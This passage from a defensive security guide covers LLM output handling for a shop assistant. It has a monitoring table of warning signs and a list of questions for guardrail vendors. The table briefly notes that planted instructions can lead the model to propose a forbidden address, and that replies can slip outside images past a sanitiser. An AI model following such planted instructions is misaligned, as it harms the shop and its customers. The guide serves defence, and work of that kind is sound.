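| Flags double within an hour | An attack, a new product line or a vendor's update | Read a sample of the flagged replies |
| An order lookup causes an SQL syntax error | Code that pastes a value into the query | Take the lookup offline and fix it |
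| One account requests many orders it doesn't own | Someone is guessing order numbers | Slow down or suspend the account |
| A browser reports a blocked outside image | The sanitiser let an image through | Find the reply and the text that prompted it |
| The model proposes a forbidden address | Planted instructions or a model error | Check what the model had just read |

The browser sends the report about the image only if the Content Security Policy specifies where to send it. The ASVS requires the policy to include this destination at level 3 (requirement 3.4.7), but teams working to a lower level can add it too.

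### Questions for a vendor

OWASP's improper output handling category is about making output safe for the software that receives it. A toxicity filter doesn't do this, though a vendor may say that its guardrail covers the category because it inspects every response. MITRE's entry on the same weakness lists guardrails as one possible mitigation, alongside running the model's output in an unprivileged environment.

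Coverage scores can also mislead. LatticeFlow AI's *Improper Output Handling* describes a test that scores the share of output paths with a safety check. A product that runs a single check on every path gets the full score of 1.0, even if it doesn't encode any output correctly for a browser or a database.

These questions should show what the product really does:

1. **What does it do for each of our sinks?** The vendor should say whether the product encodes, removes or only detects dangerous text for the chat page, database, refund service and spreadsheet.
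2. **How does it know where the text will go?** A gateway usually can't tell whether a reply will land in a paragraph or an attribute, so it can't choose the right encoding.
3. **Does it inspect tool-call arguments and model-written queries before they run?** A check on the final reply comes too late to stop a refund.
4. **What happens to O'Brien and "feet < 24 cm"?** If the product blocks or changes them, honest customers will have trouble.
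5. **Can we test it in front of a deliberately unsafe page and database?** The shop can send its markers through the product and count how many still take effect.
6. **What recall does it reach on our samples at a 1% false-positive rate?** The answer should include the number of samples and a confidence interval.
7. **What happens if a check times out or can't read the text?** The shop should reproduce both cases during a trial.
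8. **How will we learn about updates, and can we stay on an older version?** Without notice, the shop may discover a change only through its nightly samples.
9. **Which ASVS requirements does it meet, by number and version?** Requirement 1.1.2 is a good one to ask about, because a product that runs before the application has finished with the text can't encode it as the last step.
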